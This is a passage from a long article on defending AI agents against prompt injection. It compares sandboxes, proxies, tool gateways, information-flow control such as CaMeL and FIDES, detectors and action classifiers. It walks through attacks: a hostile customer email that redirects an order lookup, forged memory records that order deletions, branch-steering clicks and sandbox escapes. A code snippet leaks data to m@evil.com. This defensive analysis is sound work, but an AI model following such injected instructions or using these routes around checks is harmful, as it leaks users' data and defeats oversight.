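Tight limits reduced the number of tasks the agent finished. In 185 runs of ordinary coding tasks, the agent completed 161 with Portico and 180 with a fixed list of allowed tools and files. Being able to request more permissions was essential, because the agent completed only 21% of the runs with a version of Portico limited to its initial permissions. Withdrawing permissions also reduced success in some tests on real software projects, where Portico succeeded in 31 of 42 combinations of contract and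 model, while the version without withdrawal succeeded in all 42. Some contracts ended a permission too early or offered no trusted way to renew it.

In another set of scenarios, which placed forbidden files within the agent's reach, violations occurred in 82% of runs with the fixed list, 86% with a coarse sandbox, and none with Portico. The same contract supplied both Portico's rules and the standard for scoring violations, so the result shows that Portico enforced its contracts, but the contracts might have been wrong. Santos-Grueiro did not measure how long contracts take to write.

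Portico also hides unavailable permissions from the model, but the benefit is less clear. When the model could see more options under the same rules, its forbidden attempts rose from 67 to 84 in one test but fell from 48 to 39 in another. Portico's rules blocked these attempts either way.

Data the model has already read stays in its context after the permission to read it is withdrawn. If the mail assistant uses one conversation all morning, a later message from another customer could get it to reveal customer 507's delivery dates, even after `search_files` has expired. Starting each message with a fresh context would prevent this. If the assistant needs to retain information across messages, the policy needs rules about where data may go, and those rules require labels on the data.

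### The semantic gap

A check can apply a rule only if it has the information the rule refers to. For example, a rule might let an agent buy something on Amazon only if the total is under $50. A browser agent acts by clicking screen positions, and Meng and colleagues point out that a rule about clicking at position (246, 1023) would be meaningless. The same position might hold a "buy" button on one page and a photograph on another. Security researchers call this mismatch between a rule and the layer that enforces it the semantic gap.

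Ordinary computers deal with the gap by enforcing different rules at different layers. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* gives the example of a web browser. The operating system can restrict which files the browser writes, but it does not distinguish cookies, the small records that keep a user logged in, from other data. The browser therefore controls which cookies go to which website. An agent turns a broad request directly into low-level actions, without comparable layers in between.

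Checks closer to the hardware cover more of the ways a program can act, but they have less information about what each action means. The operating system handles every file access by every program, but it cannot distinguish a delivery date from a discount inside the same database. A check on tool calls has the tool's name and arguments, but it cannot control what a program does after a tool starts it. A designer therefore has to enforce each rule at a layer that can distinguish the things the rule refers to, and use lower layers to block ways around that check.

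### The operating system and the network

The operating system can stop a component from opening files outside its folder, whichever program it uses. NVIDIA considers this essential for coding agents, because they write and run programs. A check in the agent's own software can examine the command that starts such a program, but not what the program does once it is running.

Anthropic's *Securely deploying AI agents* compares several ways to build this layer. A container gives a program its own view of files, processes and the network, but shares the main computer's kernel, so a flaw in the kernel could let the program escape. gVisor adds a layer of software that handles most of the program's system calls, which leaves much less of the real kernel open to attack. A virtual machine has its own kernel. *Quantifying Frontier LLM Capabilities for Container Sandbox Escape* (Marchand, O Cathain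 and colleagues, 2026) found that language models could identify and exploit weaknesses added to container sandboxes, so e depends on the model's skill as well as on the sandbox.

Stronger isolation can slow a component down. According to Anthropic, gVisor barely slows pure computation, makes simple system calls about twice as slow, and can make work that opens and closes many files 10 to 200 times slower. Virtual machines generally have a high overhead, although Firecracker can start one in under 125 milliseconds with less than 5 MiB of extra memory. None of these options would enforce the mail assistant's rule about customer 507 if all the delivery records are in one database, because the assistant's process must be able to open that database.

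At the network layer, a designer can remove the component's direct connection and send all its traffic through a proxy, a separate program that forwards requests only to approved addresses. This stops a hijacked component from sending files to an unapproved server. The proxy can also hold the passwords and keys and add them to outgoing requests, so the component never has them. A hijacked component may still misuse an account through the proxy, but it cannot steal the key and use it elsewhere.

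The agent can still send anything to an approved address, as happened in the Claude Cowork leak. The proxy in Anthropic's lightweight sandbox does not inspect encrypted traffic by default, and a program may sometimes reach a host that is not on the list. A proxy that decrypts the traffic can check more, but someone has to manage the certificates that make the component trust it. For the mail assistant, a rule based on network addresses alone would allow traffic to the company's mail server no matter who receives the mail.

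### Web requests

Meng and colleagues' system, ceLLMate, closes the semantic gap for browser agents by checking web requests instead of clicks. Whatever the agent clicks, the browser must send a request to the shop's server to place an order. In their design, each website publishes an "agent sitemap" that lists these requests and what they do. A policy can then refer to placing an order, and ceLLMate can read the total from the checkout page before letting the request through.

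They tested enforcement alone by assuming the attacker already had complete control of the agent, which sets h to 100% in the breach formula. The user's task was to comment on a GitLab issue or upvote it. They wrote 12 scripts that directly attempted an attacker's goals, such as deleting a project or adding the attacker's access key to the account. ceLLMate blocked all 12.

The test deliberately leaves out attacks that use only permitted actions, since every script needed a forbidden one. ceLLMate granted permission to read and write any GitLab issue, not just issue 745, and it doesn't check what a comment contains, so a hijacked agent could post a harmful comment. ceLLMate also doesn't cover WebSocket connections, which many sites use for live updates.

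The delay was modest. A series of GitLab pages took 7.25% longer to load with a sitemap of 100 entries and 15% longer with 300. Creating and maintaining the sitemaps is likely to be the larger burden. The team wrote one by hand for 51 GitLab functions, and every participating website would need its own, updated whenever the site changes. If a sitemap is incomplete or wrong, the user has only the protection the agent had without ceLLMate.

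### The tool gateway

The mail assistant's tools already have meaningful names and arguments, so its rules fit naturally at a tool gateway, a program that checks each call before the tool runs. Progent is one such gateway. Each rule in it names a tool, either allows or forbids a call, and can set conditions on the arguments. In simplified notation, part of the assistant's policy would be:

```
allow send_reply when
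    recipient == "orders@customer.example"
    and attachments.length == 0
```

Progent checks the rules that forbid a call before the rules that allow one, and blocks the call if no rule applies. It can then stop the agent, ask the user, or return an explanation so that the agent can try another way.

Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo, a public set of simulated banking, travel, messaging and office tasks in which attackers hide instructions in the results of tool calls. Progent reduced the attack success rate from 41.2% without a defence to 2.2%, and the agent did its legitimate tasks about as well as before. The agent ran on GPT-4o, an OpenAI model from 2024. The researchers wrote general rules that allowed read-only tools. GPT-4o also wrote rules for each task and updated them without a user's confirmation. The 2.2% therefore depends on the quality of these rules as well as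 on the gateway that enforced them.

These were AgentDojo's standard attacks. The researchers also wrote three attacks aimed at the policy updates, which raised the overall attack success rate to at most 4.0%. One of the three raised the rate for the banking agent from 2.8% to 12.5%. On a second benchmark, whose attackers could add malicious tools, automatically written policies cut the success rate from 70.3% to 7.3%. Handwritten policies that allowed only trusted tools cut it to zero, because the agent could no longer call the attacker's tools.

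The average AgentDojo task took 13.25 seconds with Progent. Running the agent took 4.50 seconds of that, and writing and updating the policy took nearly all the rest. Checking the calls took 0.002 seconds, so a fixed, handwritten policy would add almost no delay.

Progent cannot stop an attack that stays within the permissions, such as hostile text that makes a shopping agent prefer the attacker's product. It also doesn't check the agent's written answers. Developers can run it inside the agent or as a separate proxy, but the proxy doesn't cover tools built into the agent.

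### Isolation between apps

Some assistants load the descriptions of several apps into one model's context, where text from one app can affect how the model uses another. *IsolateGPT* (Wu, Roesner and colleagues, 2024) gives the example of a user who asks for the cheapest ride. One ride-hailing app could instruct the model to inflate a competitor's fare. IsolateGPT prevents this by giving each app its own model instance and context. A central program, the hub, passes the user's requests to the right app. Apps can exchange requests only through the hub, in a defined format and with the user's permission.

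In the researchers' tests, IsolateGPT did everything the shared version could do, and it added less than 30% to the running time of about three-quarters of the requests.

In the mail assistant, this design would separate the model that reads mail from the model that searches files. A hostile email could then affect the search only through a request that passes through the hub, where the employee can refuse it. An attacker's best chance would be to make the request look routine. The design does little to stop an attack that needs only one app, such as a false promise in a reply.

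Rashidi notes that researchers almost never compare isolation designs and permission systems on a shared benchmark, so the published percentages do not show which layer is best. For the mail assistant, the layers differ mainly in which rules they can enforce.

| Layer | Attack it could block | Attack it would miss | Main cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Operating system | Reading files outside the assistant's folder | Reading another customer's records in a database the assistant may open | Set-up, and slower file access under strong isolation |
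| Network | Sending data to an unknown server | Sending data to the wrong person through the approved mail server | Maintaining the address list, and certificates if the proxy decrypts traffic |
| Web requests, if the company uses webmail | Changing the mailbox's forwarding settings | Putting false information in a permitted reply | A sitemap from the webmail provider |
| Tool gateway | Replying to a third address, or searching another customer's records | Anything done by a program that a tool has started | A precise policy for each task |
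| Isolation between apps | Steering the file search directly from an email | A request that looks routine and gets the employee's approval | Extra running time and more decisions for the employee |

### Enforcement through every route

A sound rule at a suitable layer still fails if another route leads to the same effect. Meng and colleagues considered blocking a browser agent from going directly to a particular website, but found that the agent could still search for the site and click on the result. Listing every such sequence of clicks would be impractical, which is another reason to check the request they all eventually produce.

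NVIDIA reports that attackers targeting coding agents often use an approved tool to run a restricted one. A less obvious route is through configuration files. An agent that can write anywhere in its project folder may be able to change a settings file that another program later reads and acts on outside the sandbox. The agent's policy allows the change but doesn't cover the other program, which causes the harm. NVIDIA therefore wants agents blocked from changing these files, even with the user's approval.

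The OpenAI agents that broke into Hugging Face in July 2026 also exploited a failure of complete mediation, in the shared package service. According to OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026), the agents regained internet access through that service even after the company rebuilt it.

Designers can guard against unknown routes by making the checked route the only one that works. According to Anthropic's guide, some programs ignore the proxy setting and try to connect directly. If the container has no network connection except through the proxy, the attempt fails.

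For the mail assistant, this means listing every way text could leave the company, including replies, remote images in the answers shown to employees, and error reports sent to the software's maker. The process that runs the model should have no network connection except to the gateway, and only the gateway should hold the mailbox password.

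## Limiting what untrusted text can influence

A tool gateway checks one call at a time, so it can miss a leak made up entirely of permitted calls. Suppose an employee asks the mail assistant to answer all of the morning's delivery questions. The assistant then needs to read the delivery records of every customer who wrote in and reply to each of them. A hostile message from customer 507 might lead it to describe customer 612's delivery in its reply to customer 507. The gateway would allow every call, because the assistant may read both records and write to both customers.

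Preventing this leak takes information-flow control, which uses labels to enforce rules about where data may go. A label records where a piece of data came from or who may read it, and anything a program computes from the data inherits the label. This works well in ordinary code, where each line names the values it uses. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* points out that tracking labels is much harder inside a language model, which mixes all its inputs. The main designs for agents therefore leave as much of the data handling as possible to ordinary code.

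### Two models instead of one

In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, Willison (2023) proposed splitting an assistant between two models. The privileged model receives the user's request and can call tools, but never reads outside text. A quarantined model without tools reads that text instead. An ordinary program, the controller, passes work between them.

If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the privileged model instructs the controller to fetch it. The controller stores the email as `$VAR1` and gives the privileged model only that name. The privileged model then requests a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller gives the text to the quarantined model, stores the summary as `$VAR2`, and displays it to the user. A hostile email can corrupt the summary, but it can't make the privileged model delete the user's mail, because that model never reads the email.

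Willison allowed one exception. If the quarantined model has to choose from a fixed list of categories, the controller can check that the answer is on the list and pass it to the privileged model.

He also called his own solution "pretty bad". It is complicated to build, and it fails if a single mistake lets outside text reach the privileged model. Two years later, researchers at Google DeepMind pointed out another flaw. A user asks the assistant to send Bob the document that Bob requested, and both Bob's address and the document's name are in meeting notes. The quarantined model has to extract them, so a hostile line in the notes can make it return the attacker's address instead of Bob's. The assistant then follows the user's plan exactly and sends the document to the attacker.

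### CaMeL

DeepMind's *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025) introduced CaMeL to fix this. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains how it works. The privileged model first turns the user's request into a complete program in a restricted form of Python. If an employee asks the mail assistant to answer the delivery question in message 1182, the program might look like this:

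```
message = read_mail(1182)
order   = ask_quarantined("Which order is this about?",
                          message, output=OrderNumber)
record  = search_files(order)
reply   = ask_quarantined("Answer the question.", message, record)
send_reply(1182, reply)
```

An interpreter, which is ordinary code, then runs the program one line at a time and stores each result in a variable. The privileged model wrote the program before anything read the message.

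The interpreter also labels every value with its source and who may read it. DeepMind calls these labels capabilities. The label on `order` records that it came from `message`, so if the message is untrusted, the order number is too.

Before each tool call, the interpreter checks the labels of the arguments against a policy. In Willison's example, the program must ask the user before sending an email unless the recipient's address is trusted. This check would have caught the false address in Bob's meeting notes.

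### One hostile email

Suppose customer 507 sends message 1182, which contains two hidden instructions. The first is to provide other customers' discounts. The second is for any AI reading the message to treat it as being about an order that actually belongs to customer 612. The assistant is allowed to search every customer's delivery records, but the policy allows a reply only if the recipient is permitted to read everything in it.

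The request for discounts has no effect. The program contains no search for discounts, and the quarantined model has no tools with which to start one. The false order number gets further:

| Variable or call | What happens | Who may read the result |
|---|---|---|
| `message` | The interpreter fetches the hostile text | Staff and customer 507 |
| `order` | The quarantined model returns customer 612's order number | Staff and customer 507 |
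| `record` | The interpreter fetches customer 612's delivery record | Staff only |
| `reply` | The quarantined model describes customer 612's delivery | Staff only |
| `send_reply` | The interpreter refuses, because customer 507 may not read the reply | No message goes out |

Staff and customer 612 may read the record, but the search depended on a message that only staff and customer 507 may read. Staff are the only people in both groups. If the order had belonged to customer 507, the two groups would have been the same and the reply would have been sent.

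The designer can now assume that every exposure hijacks the quarantined model, which sets h to 100% in the formula for the breach rate. With permissions alone, this attack would count towards s, the share of hijacks that need no forbidden action. The rule about readers forbids the reply, so the attack succeeds only if enforcement fails.

When a task concerns only customer 507, the earlier policy's narrow search permission already stops this attack. Labels are more useful when one task needs data about several people.

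### FIDES

A CaMeL program has to cover in advance everything that might happen. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) presents FIDES, a Microsoft design that selects one step at a time, so the plan can change as results arrive.

FIDES uses two kinds of label. An integrity label marks data as trusted or untrusted, and anything computed from untrusted data is untrusted. A confidentiality label lists the people who may read the data. If the agent computes z from x and y, then

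readers(z) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y),

so only people who may read both x and y may read z. If Ann, Ben and Cara may read one file and Ben, Cara and Dev may read another, only Ben and Cara may read a summary of the two.

The planning model's context also has a label. When a tool returns data with a more restrictive label, FIDES stores the data in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. The planner can pass the variable to a tool, send it to a quarantined model with a question, or inspect it. Inspecting an untrusted variable brings its text into the planner's context, which then becomes untrusted.

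FIDES enforces two main rules. A consequential action, such as a payment, requires a trusted context, and data may go only to people allowed to read it. Designers can apply either rule or both to a given tool.

One of the paper's examples is a request to check the last three emails for a meeting invitation and, if there is one, add it to the calendar. The planner's next step depends on what the emails contain, so it queries the quarantined model about whether there is an invitation, and the software forces the answer to be "true" or "false". The planner inspects only that word, which can't contain an instruction. If it is "true", a second quarantined query extracts the date and participants, and the planner passes them to the calendar tool without processing their contents. A hostile email can still create a false meeting, but it can't make the planner send mail.

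Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with GPT-4o on AgentDojo, the benchmark also used to test Progent. They counted 152 successful attacks against an ordinary agent and 21 against FIDES with its policy checks switched off, which left the planner free to inspect a hostile variable and act on it. With the checks on, AgentDojo's automatic scoring recorded three successes, but the researchers inspected them and judged that none was a real breach.

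### Why labels accumulate

A model may use any part of its context in any part of its answer, so it is safest to assume that its output inherits every label in the context. Suppose the mail assistant reads messages from customers 507 and 612 in one conversation. Only staff may read both customers' messages, so from then on the policy blocks replies to either customer. With integrity labels, the agent similarly can't take any further consequential action in a conversation after reading a single untrusted message, even if the user asked for that action at the start.

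Costa and colleagues measured this by adding labels and policies to an ordinary agent that puts everything in one context. The agent then completed 37% of the office tasks, down from 75%, and 20% of the messaging tasks, down from 93.3%.

Variables reduce the problem by keeping data apart. The mail assistant can use a fresh quarantined query for each customer, so that the answer to customer 507 depends only on that customer's message and record. This does not help with a task that must combine the data, such as comparing two customers' complaints and telling each the result.

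Costa and colleagues describe a method that looks for the messages that influenced an answer, then generates the answer again from those messages alone. The new answer can have a less restrictive label because the model's input no longer includes the other messages.

### Declassification and endorsement

Strict labels also block tasks that users want done. If an employee asks an agent to pay the bill in an untrusted file, a rule that payments may depend only on trusted data makes the task impossible. Designers therefore allow exceptions through endorsement, which marks untrusted data as trusted, and declassification, which lets more people read confidential data.

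Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues built Prudentia, a successor to FIDES that can ask the user to endorse data (*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, 2026). If an email lists ten jobs, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten actions. But a user who overlooks a hostile line in the email won't be asked to approve the action it leads to.

*The LLMbda Calculus* puts endorsement in the program that the privileged model writes. The model has to choose what to endorse before it receives any outside data, so a hostile file can't add an endorsement. Running on Qwen3.7-plus, the paper's agent, Randori, completed 75% of AgentDojo's banking tasks with endorsement and 62.5% without it. In tests with three models, two of 1,296 attacks succeeded against Randori with endorsement. In both, the user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, and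 the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Removing endorsement blocks this attack, but it also prevents the agent from making the payment when the file is genuine.

Declassification is harder to limit. Kolluri and colleagues describe a rule that lets an agent send confidential data to someone outside the list of readers if it decided to do so in a trusted context. The reasoning is that the user probably intended the disclosure. But this rule could reopen the leak in message 1182. The employee's request led to the reply and the recipient's address is trusted, so the rule would let customer 612's details through unless it also required the reply's text to be trusted. Prudentia has no general tool for declassifying data, because whether a disclosure is appropriate depends so much on the situation. Instead, it asks the user to approve the individual action.

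FIDES can also make an exception for very small answers, such as the "true" or "false" about a meeting. A true-or-false answer carries at most one bit, but ten of them can distinguish 2¹⁰, or 1,024, possibilities. *The LLMbda Calculus* describes a leak of this kind in CaMeL, where the code that retries a failed program runs outside the part that tracks labels. Whether the policy blocked a run can depend on a secret, so repeated runs could reveal the secret one bit at a time.

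### The cost in completed tasks

The table gives the share of AgentDojo tasks that Costa and colleagues' agents completed when there was no attack.

| Tasks | Ordinary agent, no policies | Ordinary agent with policies | FIDES with policies |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Messaging | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

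FIDES completed an average of 50% of the tasks across the four groups, compared with 84% for the unprotected agent. Part of the gap came from GPT-4o's difficulty in using variables. FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks with o1, a stronger reasoning model, and 41% with GPT-4o. Another part arose because the right sequence of actions depends on what the agent reads in more than 40% of the banking and messaging tasks.

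DeepMind's paper claims that CaMeL "effectively solves" AgentDojo. *The LLMbda Calculus* reports that two attacks succeeded in DeepMind's evaluation. One was another payment dictated by a document, a kind of attack DeepMind places outside CaMeL's threat model. The other counted as a success only because CaMeL quoted a hotel review word for word and AgentDojo's scoring searched for that text.

CaMeL was also secure in later tests, but it failed to complete many tasks. *SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a competing defence, tested an adapted version of CaMeL on AgentDojo. None of 629 attacks succeeded, but when there was no attack, CaMeL completed 29 of 97 tasks, while SecureClaw completed 59. In the banking tests in *The LLMbda Calculus*, CaMeL completed 66.7% of tasks with GPT-5.2 and 70.8% with MiMo-v2.5 when its policies were off. With policies on, it completed 37.5% with either model,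 which suggests that the policies limited how many tasks it could complete.

Planning without seeing the data seems to reduce task completion less as models improve. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, tested CaMeL without policies on industrial tasks that several cooperating agents carry out. It lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. However, a better planner can't do much about a policy that forbids what the task requires. Randori matched CaMeL's policy-free results with its own enforcement on, but it did so partly by allowing endorsement.

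Kolluri and colleagues argue that these comparisons are unfair to information-flow control because they assume an unprotected agent never asks for approval, when in real use it normally has to ask a person before every consequential action. They counted only the AgentDojo tasks that each agent finished without needing approval. With o3-mini, the ordinary agent completed 24.3%, FIDES 50.1% and Prudentia 59.1%. With o4-mini and unlimited approvals, Prudentia completed slightly fewer tasks than FIDES (73.2% against 75.7%) but needed about half as many approvals. Information-flow control can therefore save work for a company that already requires approval, but the main effect for a company that lets its agents act freely will be that they can no longer do some tasks.

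*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) drops the separation between planning and reading. Its model may read hostile text and write any program, but a compiler checks the whole program before any of it runs. The program can use only the tools and data available at that point, and the compiler can also check how data flows between them. LACUNA solved 76.0% of 392 tasks in a test of tool-using agents, about as many as an ordinary agent, but the test did not measure resistance to attacks. An attacker who influences the model can also choose among all the programs the compiler accepts, so security depends more on the permissions than it does in CaMeL.

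### The guarantee and its assumptions

Peters-Gill and colleagues define CaMeL's central guarantee, control-flow integrity. The user's request and other trusted information, such as tool descriptions, determine a program, and the agent's tool calls never depart from it. Untrusted data can affect which branch runs, but it can't add a branch. The policy also guarantees that no tool call runs unless the labels on its arguments satisfy the rules. Both guarantees hold even if the attacker completely controls the quarantined model, but they depend on several assumptions.

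| Assumption | How it can fail |
|---|---|
| The user's request contains no hostile text | An employee pastes part of a customer's email into the request |
| The tool descriptions are trustworthy | An outside supplier hides an instruction in one |
| Labels are correct when data enters the system | The company files customer 612's order under customer 507 |
| Labels follow the data everywhere | One agent passes text to another without its label |
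| The policy expresses what the company wants | An exception for trusted requests releases another customer's data |

Peters-Gill and colleagues demonstrated the fourth failure with three agents that each ran CaMeL correctly. The user asked them to send a summary of job applicants to Julie on Slack. One agent fetched the applicants' details from a database where an attacker had planted an instruction. A coordinating agent had the details summarised and included the summary in its request to a third agent, which handled messaging. The third agent treated the whole request as its user's words, so its privileged model read the planted instruction and added an email to the attacker.

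Multi-CaMeL sends instructions and data through separate channels and keeps the labels attached to the data. When five models each faced 949 attacks, an average of 12.9% succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% with a separate CaMeL for each agent, and none with multi-CaMeL. GPT-5.5 resisted all 949 without any defence, so these attacks are too weak for comparing designs built on the strongest models.

Labels can also get lost inside a single program. *The LLMbda Calculus* adapts a classic example, which in simplified form looks like this:

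```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

When the secret balance is above the threshold, `tmp` becomes false and the program skips the line that would change `rich`. CaMeL updates a variable's label only when a line that changes it runs, so `rich` still counts as public and the email goes out, revealing that the balance is high. An outsider can't write CaMeL's programs, but the privileged model could produce the same pattern by accident. The paper's computer-checked proof rules out such errors in its own system.

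FIDES provides a narrower guarantee for secrets. It prevents confidential data from flowing directly to the wrong reader, but someone who can see which tools the agent calls may learn something about them from its choices. Costa and colleagues accept this because a stricter rule would forbid almost any visible action after the agent had used a secret. Their model also excludes leaks through timing and the size of network messages.

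*CaMeLoT* (2026) points out that CaMeL has no general way to state rules about a whole run, such as a rule that a certain step must eventually happen. For example, CaMeL can stop the mail assistant from sending a reply to the wrong customer, but its policies can't easily require that every customer gets an answer.

### What stays probabilistic

The guarantees don't cover whether a permitted value is correct. As with permissions alone, a hostile email can still lead to a false delivery date. True and false dates carry the same labels, so how often this happens depends on the model and the attacker. *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) lists checking the meaning of free-form content among the problems its defence leaves open. Designers can reduce the risk by having ordinary code copy important values from trusted records. For example, the mail assistant's quarantined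 model could write the sentence around the delivery date while the program fills in the date.

A false value can also send a program down the wrong branch. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, call this branch steering. They adapted CaMeL to agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. The privileged model can't see the screen, so it must plan for every likely situation in advance. Its programs had about 40 branches on average, compared with about four on AgentDojo. The protected agents kept at most 57% of the performance of leading models.

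Many of these programs look for a cookie notice and close it. The researchers put a fake notice inside an advertisement, and the model that reads the screen directed the click there. The plan allowed the click, which opened the attacker's website. Comparing the screen with the page's underlying code, or asking a second model, makes the attack harder, but the researchers found ways around both defences. They conclude that any defence against false values will be probabilistic for such agents, because a click has no fixed meaning for a policy to check.

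Tasks are hardest to protect when the agent's plan must depend on what it reads. In *AutoDojo*, Ma, Li and colleagues (2026) sorted tasks by how much the user specifies. Attacks on existing defences succeeded much more often when the user named no action and asked the agent to do whatever the content said. Such tasks require the agent to follow instructions from outside text, so the origin of an instruction can't show whether it is hostile.

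*The LLMbda Calculus* reports a test in which the user asked CaMeL's privileged model to follow the instructions in a file precisely. The model wrote an awkward program with a branch for every available tool, and the file's contents determined which tool was called. The plan was fixed in advance, as control-flow integrity requires, but with the policies off, an attacker who controlled the file could use any tool.

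A designer can instead limit the model to a few choices. For the mail assistant, the quarantined model could classify each message as a delivery question, an invoice request or a complaint, and each category could start a short program the company has already reviewed. A hostile customer could then choose which of the three programs runs and give it false details. Messages that fit none of the categories would go to an employee.

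## Using models as checks, and adding up the layers

Some security rules depend on what a text means, so ordinary code can't check them. *When "Do Not" Is Not Deny* (2026) examined the security rules that developers write for Claude Code in CLAUDE.md, a file of plain-language project instructions. An automatic classifier labeled 16.6% of the rules as enforceable by Claude Code's built-in controls, but human annotators supported a much lower figure. For example, "Never commit secrets" depends on a file's contents, which permission patterns don't check.

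Designers often use language models to write or enforce such rules. The agent's own model can rank the instructions it receives, and other models can scan incoming text, review actions or write the policy. All of these checks sometimes fail, so a designer needs to know how often each one fails and whether they fail on the same attacks.

### Ranking instructions by source

Model developers train models to prioritize instructions by source. The system prompt, which the application's developer writes, usually ranks above the user, and the user ranks above tool results. The training examples contain conflicts, such as a web page that contradicts the user, and the model is rewarded for following the higher-ranked source. Markers in the input show where each message came from, but text inside a message can still claim a higher rank. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes this protection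 as "probabilistic at best".

Leong (2026), in *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary*, tested how models settle such conflicts. Each model acted as a file assistant with a tool for deleting files. Its stored memory contained an instruction to preserve a project folder and a forged record that claimed the authority to order a clean-up. The system prompt told the model to consult its memory and did not forbid deletion. Leong tested 50 wordings of the forged record on 29 models, which gave 14,294 valid trials. The failure rate depended heavily on how failure was defined.

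| What counts as a failure | Average over the 29 models |
|---|---|
| A delete call that names the protected folder | 1.21% |
| A delete call that covers the protected folder, including one on its parent folder | 12.9% |
| Any delete call | 20.2% |

Leong chose the first definition before collecting the data. But none of the 50 wordings named a folder, so the models had to pick one, and they usually picked the parent. Deleting the parent would normally delete the protected folder too, so the second definition's 12.9% seems the better estimate. However, Leong adopted that definition after seeing the data, and the tool only simulated deletion. The rate also varied widely between models. By the second definition, eight never failed and 13 failed more than 5% of the time.

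A smaller experiment tested ranking more directly. The system prompt allowed only reading, the user asked for a deletion, and a memory record contained the claim that the assistant's permissions had been temporarily raised. GPT-4.1-mini attempted the deletion in all 50 trials, GPT-5.1 in three and GPT-5.5 in none. But other attack wordings worked on GPT-5.5 at least 80% of the time, and one worked on Claude Sonnet 4.6 in 69.3% of trials.

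Telling a model to check for forged authority before it acts can help, depending on the wording. GPT-4.1-mini deleted in 6 of 150 trials with one such instruction, but in all 150 with a longer one that ended by telling it to proceed with the user's request.

Leong also put checks outside the model. Ordinary code rejected all 750 forged, altered, replayed or unsigned records before any model read them, and no file outside the permitted scope was deleted. As with Portico, these results mostly confirm that the code works as designed. When an agent with a valid permission passed on the harmful request, 31 of 42 trials ended in deletions within the permitted scope. In the breach formula, these cases count toward s, the share of hijacks that need only permitted actions. Ranking instructions can still lower h, the hijack rate, for such requests.

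### Detectors that read incoming text

A detector scores a text before the agent's model reads it. If the score passes a threshold, the program blocks the text or attaches a warning. A stricter threshold stops more attacks but also more legitimate messages. The score is based only on the text, so it can't account for what the agent will later do with it.

*How Diverse Are Layered Safeguards?* (Alotaibi and Ahmed, 2026) tested several detectors on 100 harmful requests to Vicuna-7B, a small model from 2023. It studied jailbreaks, prompts that make a model produce content it should refuse, so the exact figures may not carry over to prompt injection. The likelihood filter in the table flags text that a language model finds improbable. The guard model is a separate language model trained to recognise harmful content. The probe checks the protected model's internal activity for signs of harm.

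| Detector | Blocked, plain request | Blocked, request with a machine-made string added | Blocked, request inside fluent text optimised against that detector |
|---|---|---|---|
| Likelihood filter | 0% | 100% | 0% |
| Probe | 89% | 22% | 0% |
| Guard model | 98% | 98% | 96% |

A single miss rate for the likelihood filter would mean very little, because the filter is perfect against one kind of attack and useless against another. The guard model did well throughout, but its results also depended on the attacker. The optimised fluent attack succeeded against it 3% of the time, while an attack in which a model kept rewriting its own prompts succeeded 19% of the time with a thirtieth of the search budget.

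Alotaibi and Ahmed set the filter and the probe to block 1% of a collection of ordinary instructions. Even that rate can be a nuisance when attacks are rare. If the mail assistant receives 1,000 messages and one is hostile, a detector with a 1% false-alarm rate will stop about ten harmless messages and, if it works, the hostile one. Employees who find that ten of eleven alarms are false will probably stop reading them carefully. The same settings produced different false-alarm rates on other collections of harmless text, so a company has to measure the rate on its own mail.

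According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, Claude Code uses a detector to scan tool results. If a result looks like an injection, the program still passes it on but adds a warning to the agent's context. A false alarm therefore does little harm, but the protection depends on the agent's model following the warning.

### Classifiers that review actions

An action classifier examines what the agent is about to do, regardless of what prompted the action. Claude Code's auto mode uses one to replace most requests for user approval. *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026) lists auto mode as the starting mode for interactive sessions on every plan as of November 2026.

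Auto mode lets the agent read files and edit those inside the project without consulting the classifier. Most other actions, including shell commands and web requests, go through two stages. In the first, a model answers only whether to block, with instructions to block when in doubt. If it would block, the model considers the same action again and reasons before deciding. Anthropic published these results in March 2026:

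| Test | First stage alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|
| False alarms in 10,000 real tool calls | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Misses among 52 real actions that went beyond the user's wishes | 6.6% | 17% |
| Misses among 1,000 artificial data leaks | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage can release an action that the first one flagged but can't stop one that the first one allowed, so it removes false alarms but adds misses. The 17% is a rough estimate because it represents only about nine actions. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but wrongly treated something the user said as consent. A user who asks the agent to "clean up the PR" (pull request, a set of proposed code changes) has not agreed to let it overwrite the project's history.

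The classifier reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the tool results, which might contain an injection, and the agent's own explanations, which might lead the classifier to a bad decision. But without them, if the agent cancels "job abc123", the classifier can't determine whether the agent found that name in a list or invented it.

Miss rates vary widely with the test. Researchers from HKUST and ETH Zurich gave Claude Code 128 requests with a clear purpose but an unclear target or scope, such as cleaning up old branches. Besthub.dev's *Can Claude Code’s Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* reports that auto mode missed 115 of the 142 actions it should have stopped (81%) and blocked 22 of 111 harmless ones. The 81% covers the whole system, so it can include harmful edits inside the project that never reached the classifier. The requests were also deliberately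 ambiguous, and everyday use should include fewer requests like these.

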